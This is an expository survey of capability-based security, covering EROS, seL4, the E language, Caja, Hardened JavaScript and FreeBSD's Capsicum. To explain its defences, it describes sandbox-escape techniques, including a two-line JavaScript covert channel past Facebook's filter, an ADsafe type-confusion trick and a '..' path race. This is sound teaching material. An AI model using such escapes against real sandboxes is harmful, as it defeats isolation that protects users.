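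Shapiro explained the guarantee in a mailing-list exchange with Brunswick (2005), *Re: confinement with endogenous verification*. When EROS creates a subsystem, it can determine whether the subsystem will be confined, and whoever requested the subsystem can learn the answer. In a later reply, Shapiro added that the constructor's test covers only the capabilities a process starts with, so a separate argument is needed to show that no later sequence of operations can break its confinement.

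In *Verifying the EROS Confinement Mechanism*, Shapiro and Weber (2000) wrote a mathematical model of a broad class of capability systems that includes EROS, with rules for what each operation does. The set of everything a subsystem might ever change can be computed from the capabilities it holds at the start. They proved that no sequence of operations lets the subsystem change anything outside that set. The subsystem is confined if the set contains only the subsystem itself and objects that the customer has approved.

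This proof covered the design, so a bug in the kernel's code could still break confinement. It also covered only overt actions, and a program from a constructor that passes the test can still signal through its use of the processor or the disk.

### Boebert's objection

Armed forces wanted computers to enforce *multilevel secrecy*, in which every program and file has a level and information may move up but never down. A program at a high level may read files at a low level but must not write to them. The ban on writing down is known as the *star-property*. Earl Boebert argued in 1984 that an unmodified capability machine cannot enforce it. Take a program called Low that may read and write a low-level segment, and a program called High that may only read it:

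1. Low stores its capability to write the segment inside the segment itself.
2. High reads the segment, as the policy allows, and so obtains the capability.
3. High uses the capability to write a secret into the segment.
4. Low reads the secret.

The attack works if a program that reads a segment also obtains any capability stored there, with all its rights. This could happen with authorised pointers on the System/38, where pointers and data share segments. On CAP the attack fails at the start, because High cannot use its capability for reading data to fetch capabilities as well. Hydra and EROS let programs fetch capabilities through a read-only capability, but the copy that High receives in step 2 would also be read-only.

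Cohen and Jefferson described this rule nine years before Boebert's paper. Boebert's argument is sound for "unmodified" machines, meaning those that lack both protections, but it does not show that capability systems in general cannot keep secrets.

Miller and Shapiro list the star-property, confinement and revocation as policies that earlier authors had "proven" capability systems unable to enforce. They trace the mistake to analysing only how the graph of references can change and ignoring how the programs in it behave. To enforce the star-property, they place a small trusted object between the Low and High security levels. Low holds one end, which accepts only integers, and High holds the other, which only returns them, so Low can report to High but no capability can pass in either direction.

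### Three charges against capabilities

The best-known defence of capabilities is *Capability Myths Demolished*, in which Miller and colleagues answered three common criticisms. They thought the disagreement had lasted because people used "capability" for three different models, and each criticism is fair for at least one of those models.

| Charge | Model it fits | What the object-capability model adds |
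|---|---|---|
| Capabilities are equivalent to access control lists | Capabilities as rows of the access matrix | References that also identify the resource, and rules for how rights spread |
| Capabilities cannot confine a program | Capabilities as keys that anyone can copy and give away | A program needs a capability to the recipient before it can send one |
| Nobody can revoke a capability | Capabilities as keys | An owner can hand out access to an intermediary and switch that off later |

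Confinement seemed impossible when capabilities were compared to physical keys. Alice can copy a key and give it to anyone she meets, and the locksmith can't control whom she meets. Under Miller's rule of introduction, a program can pass a capability only over a connection it already has, so a factory can confine a program by starting it without any connection to the outside.

The criticism about revocation had more evidence behind it. Hydra's designers planned an intermediary called an alias, which an owner could disconnect from its object, but it was unfinished when Cohen and Jefferson wrote. Nine years later, in describing the System/38, Levy wrote that none of the earlier systems in his book had provided revocation and that revocation usually slowed down every access. The critics were therefore right about many of the systems they could use, although the capability model had always allowed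 revocation. Programmers can build the intermediary from ordinary objects, as they do in later capability languages.

### Predicting where a right can go

Judging whether a system is safe requires asking whether a particular subject could ever obtain a particular right. Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman proved in *Protection in Operating Systems* (1976) that no algorithm can answer this question for every access matrix. In their model, a system has a set of commands that each check the matrix for certain rights and then add or remove others. Commands can also create new subjects and objects.

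The proof uses the matrix to simulate a Turing machine, the standard mathematical model of a computer. Each subject stands for one cell of the machine's tape. A right that the subject has over itself records the symbol in that cell, and a right over the next subject keeps the cells in order. One further right marks the machine's position and state. Each of the machine's instructions has a matching command, so running the commands carries out the computation. Deciding whether the right for the final state ever appears therefore means deciding whether the machine ever halts, which Turing proved no algorithm can do for every machine.

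This does not mean that nobody can analyse any particular system. The difficulty comes from allowing arbitrary commands. Lipton and Snyder (1977), in *A Linear Time Algorithm for Deciding Subject Security*, studied the *take-grant* model, which resembles a capability system and has four fixed rules:

- **Take.** If X has the *take* right over Y, X can copy any right that Y holds.
- **Grant.** If X has the *grant* right over Y, X can give Y any right that X holds.
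- **Create.** X can create a new node and have any rights over it.
- **Remove.** X can give up a right that it holds.

Suppose first that every node is an active subject. X can then obtain a right over Z exactly when X already has it, or when a chain of take and grant arrows, pointing in any direction, connects X to a node that has it. A program can check this by following the arrows from X and visiting each one once, so its running time grows in proportion to the size of the graph.

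The direction of a take or grant arrow between two subjects doesn't matter, because they can cooperate to reverse it. Suppose X has the take right over Y and wants to give Y a right to read Z, but can't do so directly because it has no grant right over Y. Y creates a new node V, with take and grant rights over it. X takes from Y the right to grant to V, and gives V the right to read Z. Y then takes that right from V. The same method works for a grant arrow. Passive objects such as files can't take part in these exchanges, so the full test has to consider direction in some places, but it still runs in linear time.

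The answer is a worst case, like the bound in the notes-app example that assumed every object would pass on all it had.

### seL4 and its proofs

seL4 is a small capability kernel that researchers in Sydney developed in the 2000s. Its designers adapted the take-grant model to reason about how rights spread. Like Hydra, it stores capabilities in kernel memory and lets programs refer to them by position. It also makes memory itself subject to capabilities. When a program asks for a new kernel object, such as a process or a communication channel, it has to supply a capability to the unused memory that the object will occupy. One program therefore cannot exhaust the kernel's memory at the expense of the others. The kernel also records which capabilities descend from which, so that an owner can revoke all the copies at once.

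Klein, Elphinstone and colleagues (2009), in *seL4: Formal Verification of an OS Kernel*, proved that the seL4 kernel's C code does what its specification requires and nothing else. The kernel had about 8,700 lines of C and 600 of assembly language. The proof took about 200,000 lines, and the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL checked every step. Testing had revealed 16 defects in the C code before verification began, and verification revealed another 144.

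Functional correctness rules out crashes, endless loops and memory errors in the kernel, but it does not by itself show that the specification is secure. *seL4 Enforces Integrity* (Sewell and colleagues, 2011) later showed that a program can change only what its capabilities allow. *seL4: from General Purpose to a Proof of Information Flow Enforcement* (Murray and colleagues, 2013) proved that a suitably configured kernel stops information from passing between partitions that the policy separates. These results apply to the code, whereas Shapiro and Weber had proved their theorem for a model.

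All of the seL4 proofs rest on assumptions. The 2009 proof assumed that the compiler, the assembly code, the boot code and the hardware worked correctly. The team later removed the need to trust the compiler by checking the machine code against the C. The information-flow proof requires the machine to be divided into fixed partitions and excludes timing channels, so Lampson's program that signals by slowing the machine down would not contradict any of the theorems. The proofs also don't cover drivers, file systems or applications, which run outside the kernel. If someone gives an application too many capabilities, seL4 will let it use them.

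Designing and writing the kernel took 2.2 person-years, and the 2009 proof took about 20. Roughly nine of those went into tools and libraries that other projects could reuse. Klein and colleagues estimated that a similar proof for a new kernel would take six person-years.

AI systems can now write machine-checked proofs about software, which reduces the expert labour needed. Somebody must still choose the right property to prove and judge whether the assumptions about the hardware are true.

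### Why so few people use them

Slowness was a serious obstacle on the early machines. CAP had to follow several tables to find a word in memory, and the System/38 had to consult a user's profile whenever an owner wanted revocable access. It was less of an obstacle for the later systems. The New South Wales course notes list "fast" among the features of EROS, and seL4's designers made speed one of their main goals.

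Existing software has been the more lasting problem. Most desktop and server programs expect to open files by name with all of their user's rights. A capability system can run them in a compartment with its own copy of Unix, as KeyKOS did. This protects the rest of the machine, but the programs inside still have ambient authority over each other's files. Developers would have to rewrite the programs to get finer protection, and few will do that for a system with few users.

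A small kernel also lacks the drivers, file systems, network software and desktop that its users need, and that Unix and Windows already had. Capabilities did better where one company controlled the whole product. IBM sold the System/38 to businesses that wrote ordinary COBOL programs and had little reason to think about pointers. Levy expected it to become the most widespread machine of its kind. seL4 has been used in aircraft and other embedded systems, whose builders choose every program that runs.

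Other designers brought capabilities to existing software, through programming languages or additions to Unix such as Capsicum. CHERI, a processor technology from the University of Cambridge and SRI International, revives tagged capabilities to replace ordinary pointers in languages such as C. It exists today in research prototypes and a few early commercial designs for embedded devices.

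## Capability-safe languages: E, Caja and Hardened JavaScript

A programming language can enforce the object-capability rules inside an ordinary process, without a new kernel or processor. Each object then has its own rights, so a programmer can limit what each library or function may do. The operating system still treats the whole process as one program with its user's rights, and the language's runtime becomes part of the trusted computing base.

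### What the language has to rule out

Miller uses a few lines of C to show why memory safety comes first. The function `incr` adds one to a private counter and returns the result. Any other C code in the same process can use a bad pointer to overwrite the counter, or even the instructions of `incr`, and `incr` cannot prevent this. In a memory-safe language, where programs cannot forge references, an object with private variables can keep giving correct answers to its well-behaved clients while another client misbehaves. Miller calls this property *defensive consistency*.

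The language must also do without the global variables and ambient calls that rule out Java. *The Heart of Spritely*, by Lemmer-Webber and Farmer, adds that importing a library should not provide access to any interesting authority. In most languages, an imported library gets all of the program's authority. In 2018 an attacker gained control of `event-stream`, a popular JavaScript package for handling streams of data, and used it to try to steal bitcoins from users of a wallet app. The package needed neither the network nor the wallet's keys, and an article by Kate Sills, quoted in *The Heart of Spritely*, argues that least authority would have prevented the attack.

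Designers have usually made capability languages by removing features from existing ones. Joe-E is a subset of Java in which global variables can hold only immutable data. Emily restricts OCaml in a similar way. W7 needed fewer changes because it started from Scheme, where a function can already use only the variables visible where it is defined.

### Read-only wrappers, caretakers and membranes

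A plain reference gives its holder permanent access to all of an object's public methods. Someone who wants to grant less access passes an intermediary instead, which in these languages is an ordinary object. The examples below are in JavaScript and use `harden`, a function from Hardened JavaScript that makes an object permanently unchangeable.

A read-only wrapper offers one method and keeps the file to itself:

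```js
function makeReadOnly(file) {
  return harden({
    read() { return file.read(); }
  });
}
```

Code that holds the wrapper can call `read` but cannot reach `file`. The wrapper therefore attenuates access to the file without help from a kernel. This works only if `read` returns plain text. If `read` returned an object with methods that change the file, the wrapper would have to wrap that object too.

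Miller applies the idea to an account manager that reports a bank balance to a spreadsheet and a finance application. In the first design, one object both reports the balance and sets it, so the finance application could set a false balance and the spreadsheet would display it. Miller splits the object in two. The account manager keeps the half that sets the balance and gives its clients only the half that reports it.

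The *caretaker*, which David Redell described in 1974, is an intermediary with an off switch:

```js
function makeCaretaker(file) {
  let target = file;
  const use = () => {
    if (target === null) throw new Error("revoked");
    return target;
  };
  const caretaker = harden({
    read()      { return use().read(); },
    write(text) { use().write(text); }
  });
  const revoke = () => { target = null; };
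  return [caretaker, revoke];
}
```

Suppose Alice has a file `notes` containing "buy milk". She runs `const [bobsNotes, revoke] = makeCaretaker(notes)`, gives `bobsNotes` to Bob and keeps `revoke`.

| Who | Call | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Bob | `copy = bobsNotes.read()` | Bob has the text "buy milk" |
| Bob | `bobsNotes.write("buy eggs")` | The file now contains "buy eggs" |
| Bob | `carol.receive(bobsNotes)` | Carol can use the file too |
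| Alice | `revoke()` | The caretaker drops its reference to the file |
| Bob | `bobsNotes.read()` | Error: revoked |
| Carol | `bobsNotes.write("buy ham")` | Error: revoked |
| Bob | `copy` | Still "buy milk" |
| Alice | `notes.read()` | "buy eggs" |

Alice cuts off Carol without knowing that Bob shared his access. But she cannot take back the text Bob copied, and his change to the file stays until somebody reverses it. If the text were a password, Bob could keep using it wherever it works.

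In 2001, researchers were still repeating the claim that capabilities cannot be revoked. Miller and Shapiro explain that these researchers looked only at permissions. Bob never had permission on the file and still has permission on the caretaker, so by that measure Alice has revoked nothing, even though Bob can no longer use the file. Looking only at permissions also makes audits incomplete. In 1984, Karger and Herbert proposed giving security officers a list of every subject that may access a compromised object. Bob would not appear on it, because Alice had followed good practice and given him only indirect access.

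A caretaker guards one object. Suppose Alice gives Bob revocable access to a function `openNote`, which takes the name of a note and returns a second function for reading it. If Bob calls `openNote` in time and keeps the second function, he can read that note after Alice has revoked his access. A *membrane* closes this gap by wrapping everything that passes through it. In this small version, all capabilities are functions:

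```js
function makeMembrane(target) {
  let enabled = true;
  const wrap = (value) => {
    if (Object(value) !== value) return value;  // text, numbers
    if (typeof value !== "function") throw new Error("functions only");
    return harden((...args) => {
      if (!enabled) throw new Error("revoked");
      return wrap(value(...args.map((arg) => wrap(arg))));
    });
  };
  const revoke = () => { enabled = false; };
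  return [wrap(target), revoke];
}
```

Every wrapper checks the same `enabled` variable, so one call to `revoke` disables them all, including the function Bob kept. The membrane wraps arguments as well as results because Bob might pass in a function of his own. If `openNote` called that function with a note, the membrane would have to wrap the note too. Miller recommends membranes when Alice trusts neither side, since a caretaker fails if the object behind it gives its clients a direct reference to itself.

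A practical membrane needs more code than this. It must wrap errors, because a program can attach a reference to an error it throws. It should also recognise its own wrappers, or an object that passes out through it and back will be wrapped twice.

### E and its vats

Miller and others began developing the language E at the company Electric Communities, which released it as open source when its business plans changed. An online community continued the work. Marc Stiegler used E to build CapDesk, a desktop designed to withstand viruses, and the US defence research agency DARPA paid for a security review of both.

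Miller describes E in his thesis and argues that access control and concurrency control are parts of one problem. Access control determines which programs may affect an object, and concurrency control determines when. A program can do damage by acting on an object at the wrong moment, for example when another program has only half updated it.

E handles concurrency by grouping objects into *vats*. A vat resembles a process, with its own memory and a single thread. Objects in the same vat can call each other directly. To reach an object in another vat, a program sends a message and continues without waiting. It immediately gets a *promise*, which stands for the answer until it arrives. Each vat finishes one message before it starts the next, so no other code can interfere halfway through.

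Vats never stop to wait for each other, so two vats cannot block each other forever, as threads that use locks can. A promise can still depend on its own result, and then it never resolves. Miller knew of only two such bugs in many years of work by perhaps 60 programmers, but acknowledged that others might have gone unnoticed.

E does not protect objects in the same vat from resource exhaustion. A malicious object can stop the others from running by looping forever or using up all the memory. It cannot make them give wrong answers, though, and Miller considered this good enough for many uses because a loss of service is easy to notice and corrupted data may not be. Someone who needs more protection can put the untrusted object in its own vat, since a system can set limits on a vat as it can on a process. Even so, E cannot guarantee that a vat will keep serving its honest clients when another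 vat attacks it.

### References between machines

Within a vat, E's runtime prevents forgery. Between machines there is no shared runtime, so E uses cryptography. Suppose Alice, Bob and Carol are objects on three machines, and Alice sends Bob a reference to Carol:

1. Carol's vat has a pair of cryptographic keys, and a fingerprint of the public key serves as the vat's identity. When it first let a reference to Carol leave, it also chose a long random number to stand for her. Miller calls this a *Swiss number*, after the popular idea that anyone who knows the number of a Swiss bank account can use it.
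2. Alice's vat sends Bob's vat the identity of Carol's vat, some network addresses where it may be found, and Carol's Swiss number.
3. Bob's vat contacts one of the addresses. The machine there has to prove that it holds the private key that matches the identity.
4. Once the two vats have an encrypted connection, Bob's vat sends the Swiss number, and Carol's vat begins passing Bob's messages to her.

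Nobody can impersonate Carol's vat without its private key, or reach Carol by guessing. No central authority issues names or certificates.

The guarantees are weaker between machines than within one. A Swiss number is data, so any program that can send data can also give away a reference. Alice's machine also cannot determine what software the other machines run or what else they communicate with, so it cannot confine a program on somebody else's computer.

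Revocation becomes harder too. If Alice keeps the caretaker on her own machine, she can always switch it off, but every message from Bob to Carol must pass through her machine. If she puts it on Carol's machine, the messages go directly, but a network failure could stop her revocation order from arriving, and Bob would keep his access. Miller's remedy is a caretaker that disables itself when it loses contact with Alice, so Bob keeps his access only until the system detects the broken connection.

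### Promise pipelining and Cap'n Proto

A program that works with many small objects may need many messages to get anything done, and over a network each exchange takes time. E reduces the delay by letting a program send messages to a promise before the answer has arrived:

```
def folder := server <- openFolder("work")
def file   := folder <- openFile("plan.txt")
def text   := file   <- read()
```

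The arrow `<-` sends a message. E sends the requests for the folder, the file and the text all at once, a technique called *promise pipelining*. The second request is addressed to "whatever the first one returns", and the server fills in the folder when it has it. An ordinary remote-call system would wait for the folder before requesting the file, and for the file before requesting the text.

If a round trip takes time *L*, then *n* calls that each depend on the previous one take about *nL* without pipelining and about *L* with it, plus the server's working time in both cases. At 100 milliseconds per round trip, the three calls above take 100 milliseconds instead of 300. Faster hardware does not remove the round-trip delay, because signals cannot travel faster than light.

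The saving shrinks if the server returns a reference to an object on a third machine, because the later requests must go on to that machine. If the first request fails, requests that depend on it fail with the same error. Miller credits the technique to Barbara Liskov and Liuba Shrira, who published it in 1988 for clients calling a server. The designers of E extended it to machines that call each other in both directions.

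Kenton Varda's Cap'n Proto, a system for encoding data and making remote calls, uses a protocol based on CapTP, which was developed for E. Its documentation page *RPC Protocol* calls pipelining "time travel" but notes that a client can use a result before it arrives only in further requests to the same server. A program that has to look at a folder's contents before deciding which file to open must still wait for them.

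Pipelining also makes interfaces with many small calls practical over a network. In a benchmark, Cap'n Proto (2013) used a calculator with separate calls to add, subtract, multiply and divide two numbers. Programmers would normally avoid this design on a network and send the whole expression in one call, but with pipelining the small calls can travel together. This helps a capability system because small objects with few methods make it possible to grant narrow authority.

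Cap'n Proto also follows the rule of introduction, so a program may use any reference it receives in a message (Varda, 2014, *Cap'n Proto 0.5, and how it is central to Sandstorm*). Version 0.5 added references that a program can save to disk and restore over a later connection, a feature E also had. Varda developed Cap'n Proto as part of Sandstorm, and Cloudflare's later Cap'n Web brought a similar protocol to JavaScript. Lemmer-Webber and Farmer's Goblins, a library for writing distributed social applications, also builds on CapTP.

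### Shared built-in objects in JavaScript

JavaScript is memory-safe, and its functions can keep variables private, as the caretaker does with `target`. The problem is that all scripts in a page normally share one set of built-in objects, and any script can change them.

In 2010, Maffeis, Mitchell and Taly, in *Object Capabilities and Isolation of Untrusted Web Applications*, showed what this meant for Facebook, which let outside developers put small applications on its pages. Facebook filtered their code to keep it away from the rest of the page. Two applications could nevertheless communicate if one ran the first of these lines and the other ran the second:

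```js
({}).toString.channel = "message";
const received = ({}).toString.channel;
```

Each application creates its own empty object, `{}`, but both objects inherit the same `toString` function. The first application attaches a message to that function, which the second can read even though no reference has passed between them. Maffeis and colleagues could also change another shared function to capture values that Facebook's own code was using, and so break out of the filter altogether. They reported the problem, and Facebook began work on a fix.

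They found other holes in ADsafe, Yahoo's filter for advertisements. One of its functions created page elements and was supposed to refuse to create scripts. The function converted the requested name to text to check it, and the browser converted it again when creating the element. An advertisement could supply an object that produced "div", a harmless kind of element, the first time and "script" the second. The same kind of gap between check and use made Unix's `access` call unsafe, but exploiting this one required no careful timing.

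### Caja and what its proof covered

Google's Caja was a more thorough attempt. Web applications such as webmail usually removed all scripts from content that other people supplied. Miller, Samuel and colleagues (2008) designed Caja to let the applications run those scripts by translating each one into a restricted form of JavaScript before the browser received it.

In Cajita, the core of Caja, a script could not use global variables. Caja turned the script into a function with a parameter for every name the script used but did not define, so the page controlled what each of those names referred to. Cajita also replaced direct access to an object's properties with calls to two functions, `getPub` for reading and `setPub` for writing, which could block the access. A third function, `freeze`, made an object read-only so that several scripts could share it safely.

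Maffeis and colleagues proved that this design isolates scripts from one another. They treated a page as a series of scripts that run one after another. The scripts are isolated if none of them touches a forbidden part of memory or writes anything that a later one reads.

The authority of a script, in their definition, is a set that contains every read and write it might perform. They call a language *authority safe* if running a script *t* can affect the authority of another script *u* in only two ways:

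- If *t* writes nothing that *u* has authority to read, then *u*'s authority stays the same.
- Otherwise, *u* may gain authority, but only from what *t* had and from newly created objects.

The second condition can be written as

auth_after(*u*) ⊆ auth_before(*u*) ∪ auth_before(*t*) ∪ new

In an authority-safe language, a page can therefore check the scripts' authority once, at the start. If no script has forbidden authority at that point, and none can write to anything a later script can read, the scripts will stay isolated whatever they do. Maffeis and colleagues proved that every language that meets their definition of capability safety is authority safe, and that the core of Cajita is capability safe.

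They also proved that a second subset of JavaScript, called Js, is authority safe although it does not follow the object-capability model, so object capabilities are not the only way to isolate scripts. Js lets scripts use global variables but gives each script its own names for them, and it makes the built-in objects read-only.

The theorem about Cajita covers a simplified design and assumes that `getPub` and `setPub` follow certain rules, so a bug in Google's code could still let a script escape. The definition of isolation also doesn't cover denial of service. If the first script runs forever, the later ones never start, but the page still counts as isolated because nothing has influenced them.

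Cajita differed too much from ordinary JavaScript for developers to move existing scripts to it easily. Caja also offered Valija, a language much closer to JavaScript, and translated it into Cajita, but Maffeis and colleagues report a "hefty performance cost".

Caja also had to keep up with browsers. SecurityWeek's *Google Patches Vulnerabilities in Caja Tool* reports that Michał Bentkowski, a bug bounty hunter, found several ways past Caja that put users at risk in Google Docs, where Google relied on it to contain user-written scripts. According to an account published by Securitum, Caja's parser followed an older version of the JavaScript standard than browsers did. The parser rejected most newer code, but a bug in how it read comments let some through, and the browser then ran code that Caja had not properly examined.

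Google archived Caja on 31 January 2021. In its notice, Google said that Caja had not kept up with research on web security, and that Google engineers and outsiders had reported vulnerabilities in it. Some programs kept using it. NIST's *CVE-2021-32798* describes a flaw in Jupyter Notebook, a data analysis tool that used an outdated copy of Caja to clean up untrusted documents. A way to bypass Caja was already public, so a malicious notebook could run code on the computer of anyone who opened it.

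### Hardened JavaScript and Endo

Caja had to translate scripts because JavaScript at the time gave pages no way to freeze objects. The 2009 edition of the standard added one, along with a strict mode that removes some of the language's most dangerous features. Miller and others used these to design Secure ECMAScript, now better known as Hardened JavaScript. The browser's own engine enforces most of its rules, which leaves far less translated code to fall behind the standard.

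A program sets it up in a few lines:

```js
lockdown();
const app = new Compartment({ notes: makeReadOnly(file) });
app.evaluate("notes.read()");
```

`lockdown` freezes the built-in objects, so an attempt to attach a message to `toString` now fails. A *compartment* has its own global variables and starts with only the harmless built-ins and whatever its creator passes in. The script above can read the notes but cannot open another file or contact a server, because the names for doing so do not exist in its compartment. The creator must still be careful about what it passes in. An unfrozen object shared by two compartments would again let them communicate, so `harden` freezes an object and everything reachable from it.

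Much existing code runs unchanged, but some libraries add features to the built-in objects, which `lockdown` prevents. Others give an object its own `toString` by assignment, and this fails when the inherited version is frozen. Hardened JavaScript works around the common cases. Code that uses a global name to reach the network or the file system has to receive a reference instead, or its developers have to rewrite it.

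Compartments in one process share a thread and memory, so resource exhaustion is as much of a problem as it is in one of E's vats. The usual remedy is again to run the code in a separate process or worker that the host can stop.

Timing attacks are harder to rule out. In 2018 researchers published Spectre, an attack on the way processors guess which instructions will come next. The guesses leave traces in the processor's cache, and by timing memory accesses, a program can work out data elsewhere in its process that it holds no reference to. Language rules about references don't close this kind of channel. Hardened JavaScript makes timing harder by withholding the clock from compartments by default, but a program may still find a substitute, such as exchanging messages with a server that knows the time. Secrets are therefore safer in a different process from untrusted code.

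Most engines lack built-in compartments, so programs load them from a library. The cryptocurrency wallet MetaMask uses Hardened JavaScript to confine add-ons and the packages it depends on, the kind of protection the victims of `event-stream` lacked. The company Agoric, where Miller became chief scientist, uses Hardened JavaScript to run contracts on a blockchain.

The library is part of Endo, an open-source project that, by its own account, grew out of Miller's work on E, Caja and Secure ECMAScript. Another of its leading developers is Kris Kowal, who wrote the first widely used JavaScript library for promises. The project belongs to the Decentralized Cooperation Foundation. Endo also includes a version of CapTP and a background program that runs guest programs in separate worker processes and tracks the references each one holds. A user can run an AI agent's code there like any other guest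 program, and the code starts with no access to the user's files or accounts.

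## Capsicum and WASI: capabilities for existing programs

Few developers will rewrite existing C and C++ programs in a capability language. Capsicum and WASI let them use capabilities in these programs with less work. Capsicum adds capabilities to the kernel of FreeBSD, a free Unix system. WASI is a new system interface that developers can target by recompiling existing code.

### Capability mode

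*Capsicum* (Watson, Anderson and colleagues, 2010) starts from the Unix file descriptor, which is already close to a capability. But ordinary descriptors don't confine a process, because it can always open more files by name. They also allow too much, since a program can change a file's access permissions even through a descriptor opened only for reading.

Capsicum addresses the first problem with *capability mode*. A process enters this mode by calling `cap_enter`, and from then on the kernel denies it access to every *global namespace*, meaning any set of names that all programs share, such as file paths, process numbers and network addresses. The process can never leave capability mode, and any process it starts is in the mode too. The original process keeps the descriptors it already has, and other processes can send it more.

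Capsicum addresses the second problem by attaching a list of rights to a descriptor. The 2010 version defined about 60 rights, such as reading, writing and moving to another position in the file. A program can remove rights from a descriptor but cannot add any. In an example from the FreeBSD manual, a program keeps the rights to read and write a file but gives up the right to call `fchmod`, which changes the file's permissions. The kernel checks rights in the function that turns a descriptor's number into an open file.

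A descriptor can also refer to a directory and give access to the files below it. If descriptor 4 refers to `/lib`, a process in capability mode can open `libc.so.7` relative to descriptor 4, but not `/etc/passwd` or `../etc/passwd`.

The 2010 design rejected every path containing "..", even one that seemed to stay inside the directory. MIT's lecture notes show why, with a process that may use only `/foo`:

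1. One thread starts in `/foo/a` and opens the path `b/c/../..`, which should lead back to `/foo/a`.
2. When the kernel has got as far as `c`, another thread moves `c` up to `/foo/d`.
3. The first ".." now leads to `/foo` and the second to `/`, so the process has escaped.

This is another race between a check and a use, like the one that made `access` unsafe.

### tcpdump before and after

The program `tcpdump` captures network packets and prints a description of each. It interprets untrusted data in many complicated formats, and its parsing code has a long history of security bugs. Before Capsicum, an attacker who sent a packet that exploited such a bug gained all the rights of the user running `tcpdump`, often the administrator.

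The program opens the capture device first and then processes packets in a loop, so Watson and colleagues could add the call between the two steps. Slightly simplified, the change looks like this:

```c
  pd = pcap_open_live(device, ...);   /* open the capture device */
+ if (cap_enter() < 0)
+     error("cap_enter failed");
  status = pcap_loop(pd, ...);        /* read and print packets */
```

After these two lines, the parser can no longer open a file or contact another machine. It still holds the descriptors that `tcpdump` had open, including the user's terminal, from which it could read key presses. Six more lines narrowed those:

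| Descriptor | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Keyboard input | Read key presses | Ask for the file's status only |
| Normal output and error messages | Every operation on an open file | Write, change position, ask for status |
| Capture device | Read packets, send packets | The same |
| Any other file the user can open | Open by name | No access |

An attacker who takes over the parser can still read the captured traffic and print false descriptions of it. In this version the attacker could also send packets, because the capture device stayed open for writing.

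The change also broke `tcpdump`'s lookup of names for the machines whose packets it prints. The library that does this reads a configuration file on the first lookup, and by then the process was in capability mode and could not open the file. Watson and colleagues switched to a resolver that passes lookups to a separate local program. FreeBSD later generalized this fix in Casper, a set of helper services that act for sandboxed programs. A program connects to Casper before entering capability mode and sends it requests afterwards.

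According to the page on the University of Cambridge's *Capsicum*, `tcpdump` still did not enter the sandbox if the user chose the option that runs another command on each finished capture file, or the one that reads a list of file names.

### Lines changed and time lost

Watson and colleagues adapted four programs:

| Program | Lines added or changed | Reason for the amount |
|---|---|---|
| `tcpdump` | 2, or 8 with narrower descriptors | Opens what it needs, then works in a loop |
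| `dhclient`, which obtains a network address | 2 | Already ran its risky part in a separate process |
| Chromium, a web browser | About 100 | Already ran pages in separate processes |
| `gzip`, which compresses files | 409, about 16% of its source | Needed splitting into two processes |

The `gzip` figure is the best guide for an ordinary program. One process now opens the files, and the other compresses the data and holds only the descriptors for input and output. Most of the new code passes requests between them. At first the divided program ran faster than the original because the user's choice of compression level never reached the second process, which used the wrong setting. The compiler could not detect the mistake because the variable for the level existed in both processes.

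Chromium's developers had already built sandboxes for other systems, which allowed a comparison of methods. Each was meant to stop a malicious web page from reaching the user's files.

| System and method | Lines of code | Weaknesses that Watson and colleagues found |
|---|---|---|
| Windows, access control lists | 22,350 | Pages can still use the network and many USB sticks |
| Linux, `chroot` (a restricted view of the file system) | 605 | Network stays open; needs a helper with full system rights |
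| Mac OS X, Seatbelt | 560 | Broad rights; policy separate from the program |
| Linux, SELinux | 200 | All sandboxes share one set of rights and can read all of `/etc` |
| Linux, seccomp | 11,301 | Pages can read any file the user can |
| FreeBSD, Capsicum | 100 | None listed |

This comparison comes from Capsicum's own designers, and lines of code are a rough measure of effort and a poor measure of security. The seccomp figure is also out of date. In 2010 seccomp allowed a process to do little more than read, write and exit, so Chromium's developers had to route everything else through a trusted thread. Linux later let programs supply their own filters, which decide whether to allow each system call.

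Capsicum added little overhead in the tests. On a 1.86 GHz server, using a restricted descriptor added about 0.06 microseconds to each operation, or 4% to 10% for the calls measured. Entering capability mode took 1.2 microseconds, and neither `tcpdump` nor `dhclient` became noticeably slower. Creating a separate sandboxed process, exchanging one message with it and closing it took about 1.5 milliseconds. The divided `gzip` took an extra 2.4 milliseconds per run, which hardly matters for files larger than about 500 kilobytes.

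Watson and colleagues thought the largest remaining problem was programming effort. Dividing a program means writing a small distributed system, and the programmer has to judge where a division would improve security.

### Use on FreeBSD

FreeBSD has included Capsicum by default since version 10.0, and the system's own programs use it. The daemon that receives audit records from other machines can add to its files but cannot alter records it has already stored. The tool that signs boot software examines untrusted files in a process that has no access to the signing key. OpenSSH, the standard program for remote logins, uses Capsicum on FreeBSD to restrict the process that checks credentials.

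Few other developers have followed. Alhindi and Hallett (2024), in *Sandboxing Adoption in Open Source Ecosystems*, searched the source code of 30,763 FreeBSD packages in 2023 and found Capsicum in 43 (0.14%). The count excludes programs that come with FreeBSD, but on a freshly installed machine only 3 of the 47 running processes used Capsicum.

On OpenBSD, a related system, 33 of 36 processes were sandboxed. Its developers use two simpler calls, `pledge` and `unveil`, which let a program list the groups of operations and the directories it will need. However, only about 1.5% of add-on packages used them. OpenBSD's developers could adapt their own programs, but nobody could make outside developers do the same, and a simple interface was not enough to persuade them.

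The amount of code doesn't explain Capsicum's low use either. In `gmid`, a small server, the sandbox takes 28 lines with Capsicum, 96 with `pledge` and `unveil`, and 549 with seccomp. But child processes inherit Capsicum's restrictions, and `gmid` starts scripts that may need more access than the server. Its developer had to split the program in two and leave the half that runs scripts outside the sandbox, whereas `pledge` could restrict both halves.

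Each system also has its own interface. *Playing in the Sandbox* (2025) describes developers writing much the same restrictions again with different tools and getting different sandboxes, even for simple programs.

### Why Linux did not adopt Capsicum

Drysdale (2014), in *Adding FreeBSD's Capsicum security framework (part 1)*, proposed the descriptor rights for Linux. The kernel turns a descriptor into an open file in about 100 places, and each had to be marked with the rights it required. The patches touched 118 files. Corbet (2014), in *Capsicum for Linux*, expected resistance to the size of the change and questions about why Linux needed a second sandbox when seccomp filters could in theory do the same job.

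Biederman (2014), in *Adding FreeBSD's Capsicum security framework*, made the more basic objection that Unix descriptors were already capabilities, so any further restriction should go on the open file itself rather than in an extra layer above it. He also complained that Capsicum had no way to revoke access, and suggested giving a sandboxed process its own small file system instead of checking paths.

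In the same thread, Bonzini (2014) defended the extra layer. Two processes may share one open file but need different rights to it, as when a child process may only write to a channel that its parent can also read. A restriction on the file itself would apply to both processes. In capability terms, Bonzini was defending attenuation, which requires rights to belong to the reference.

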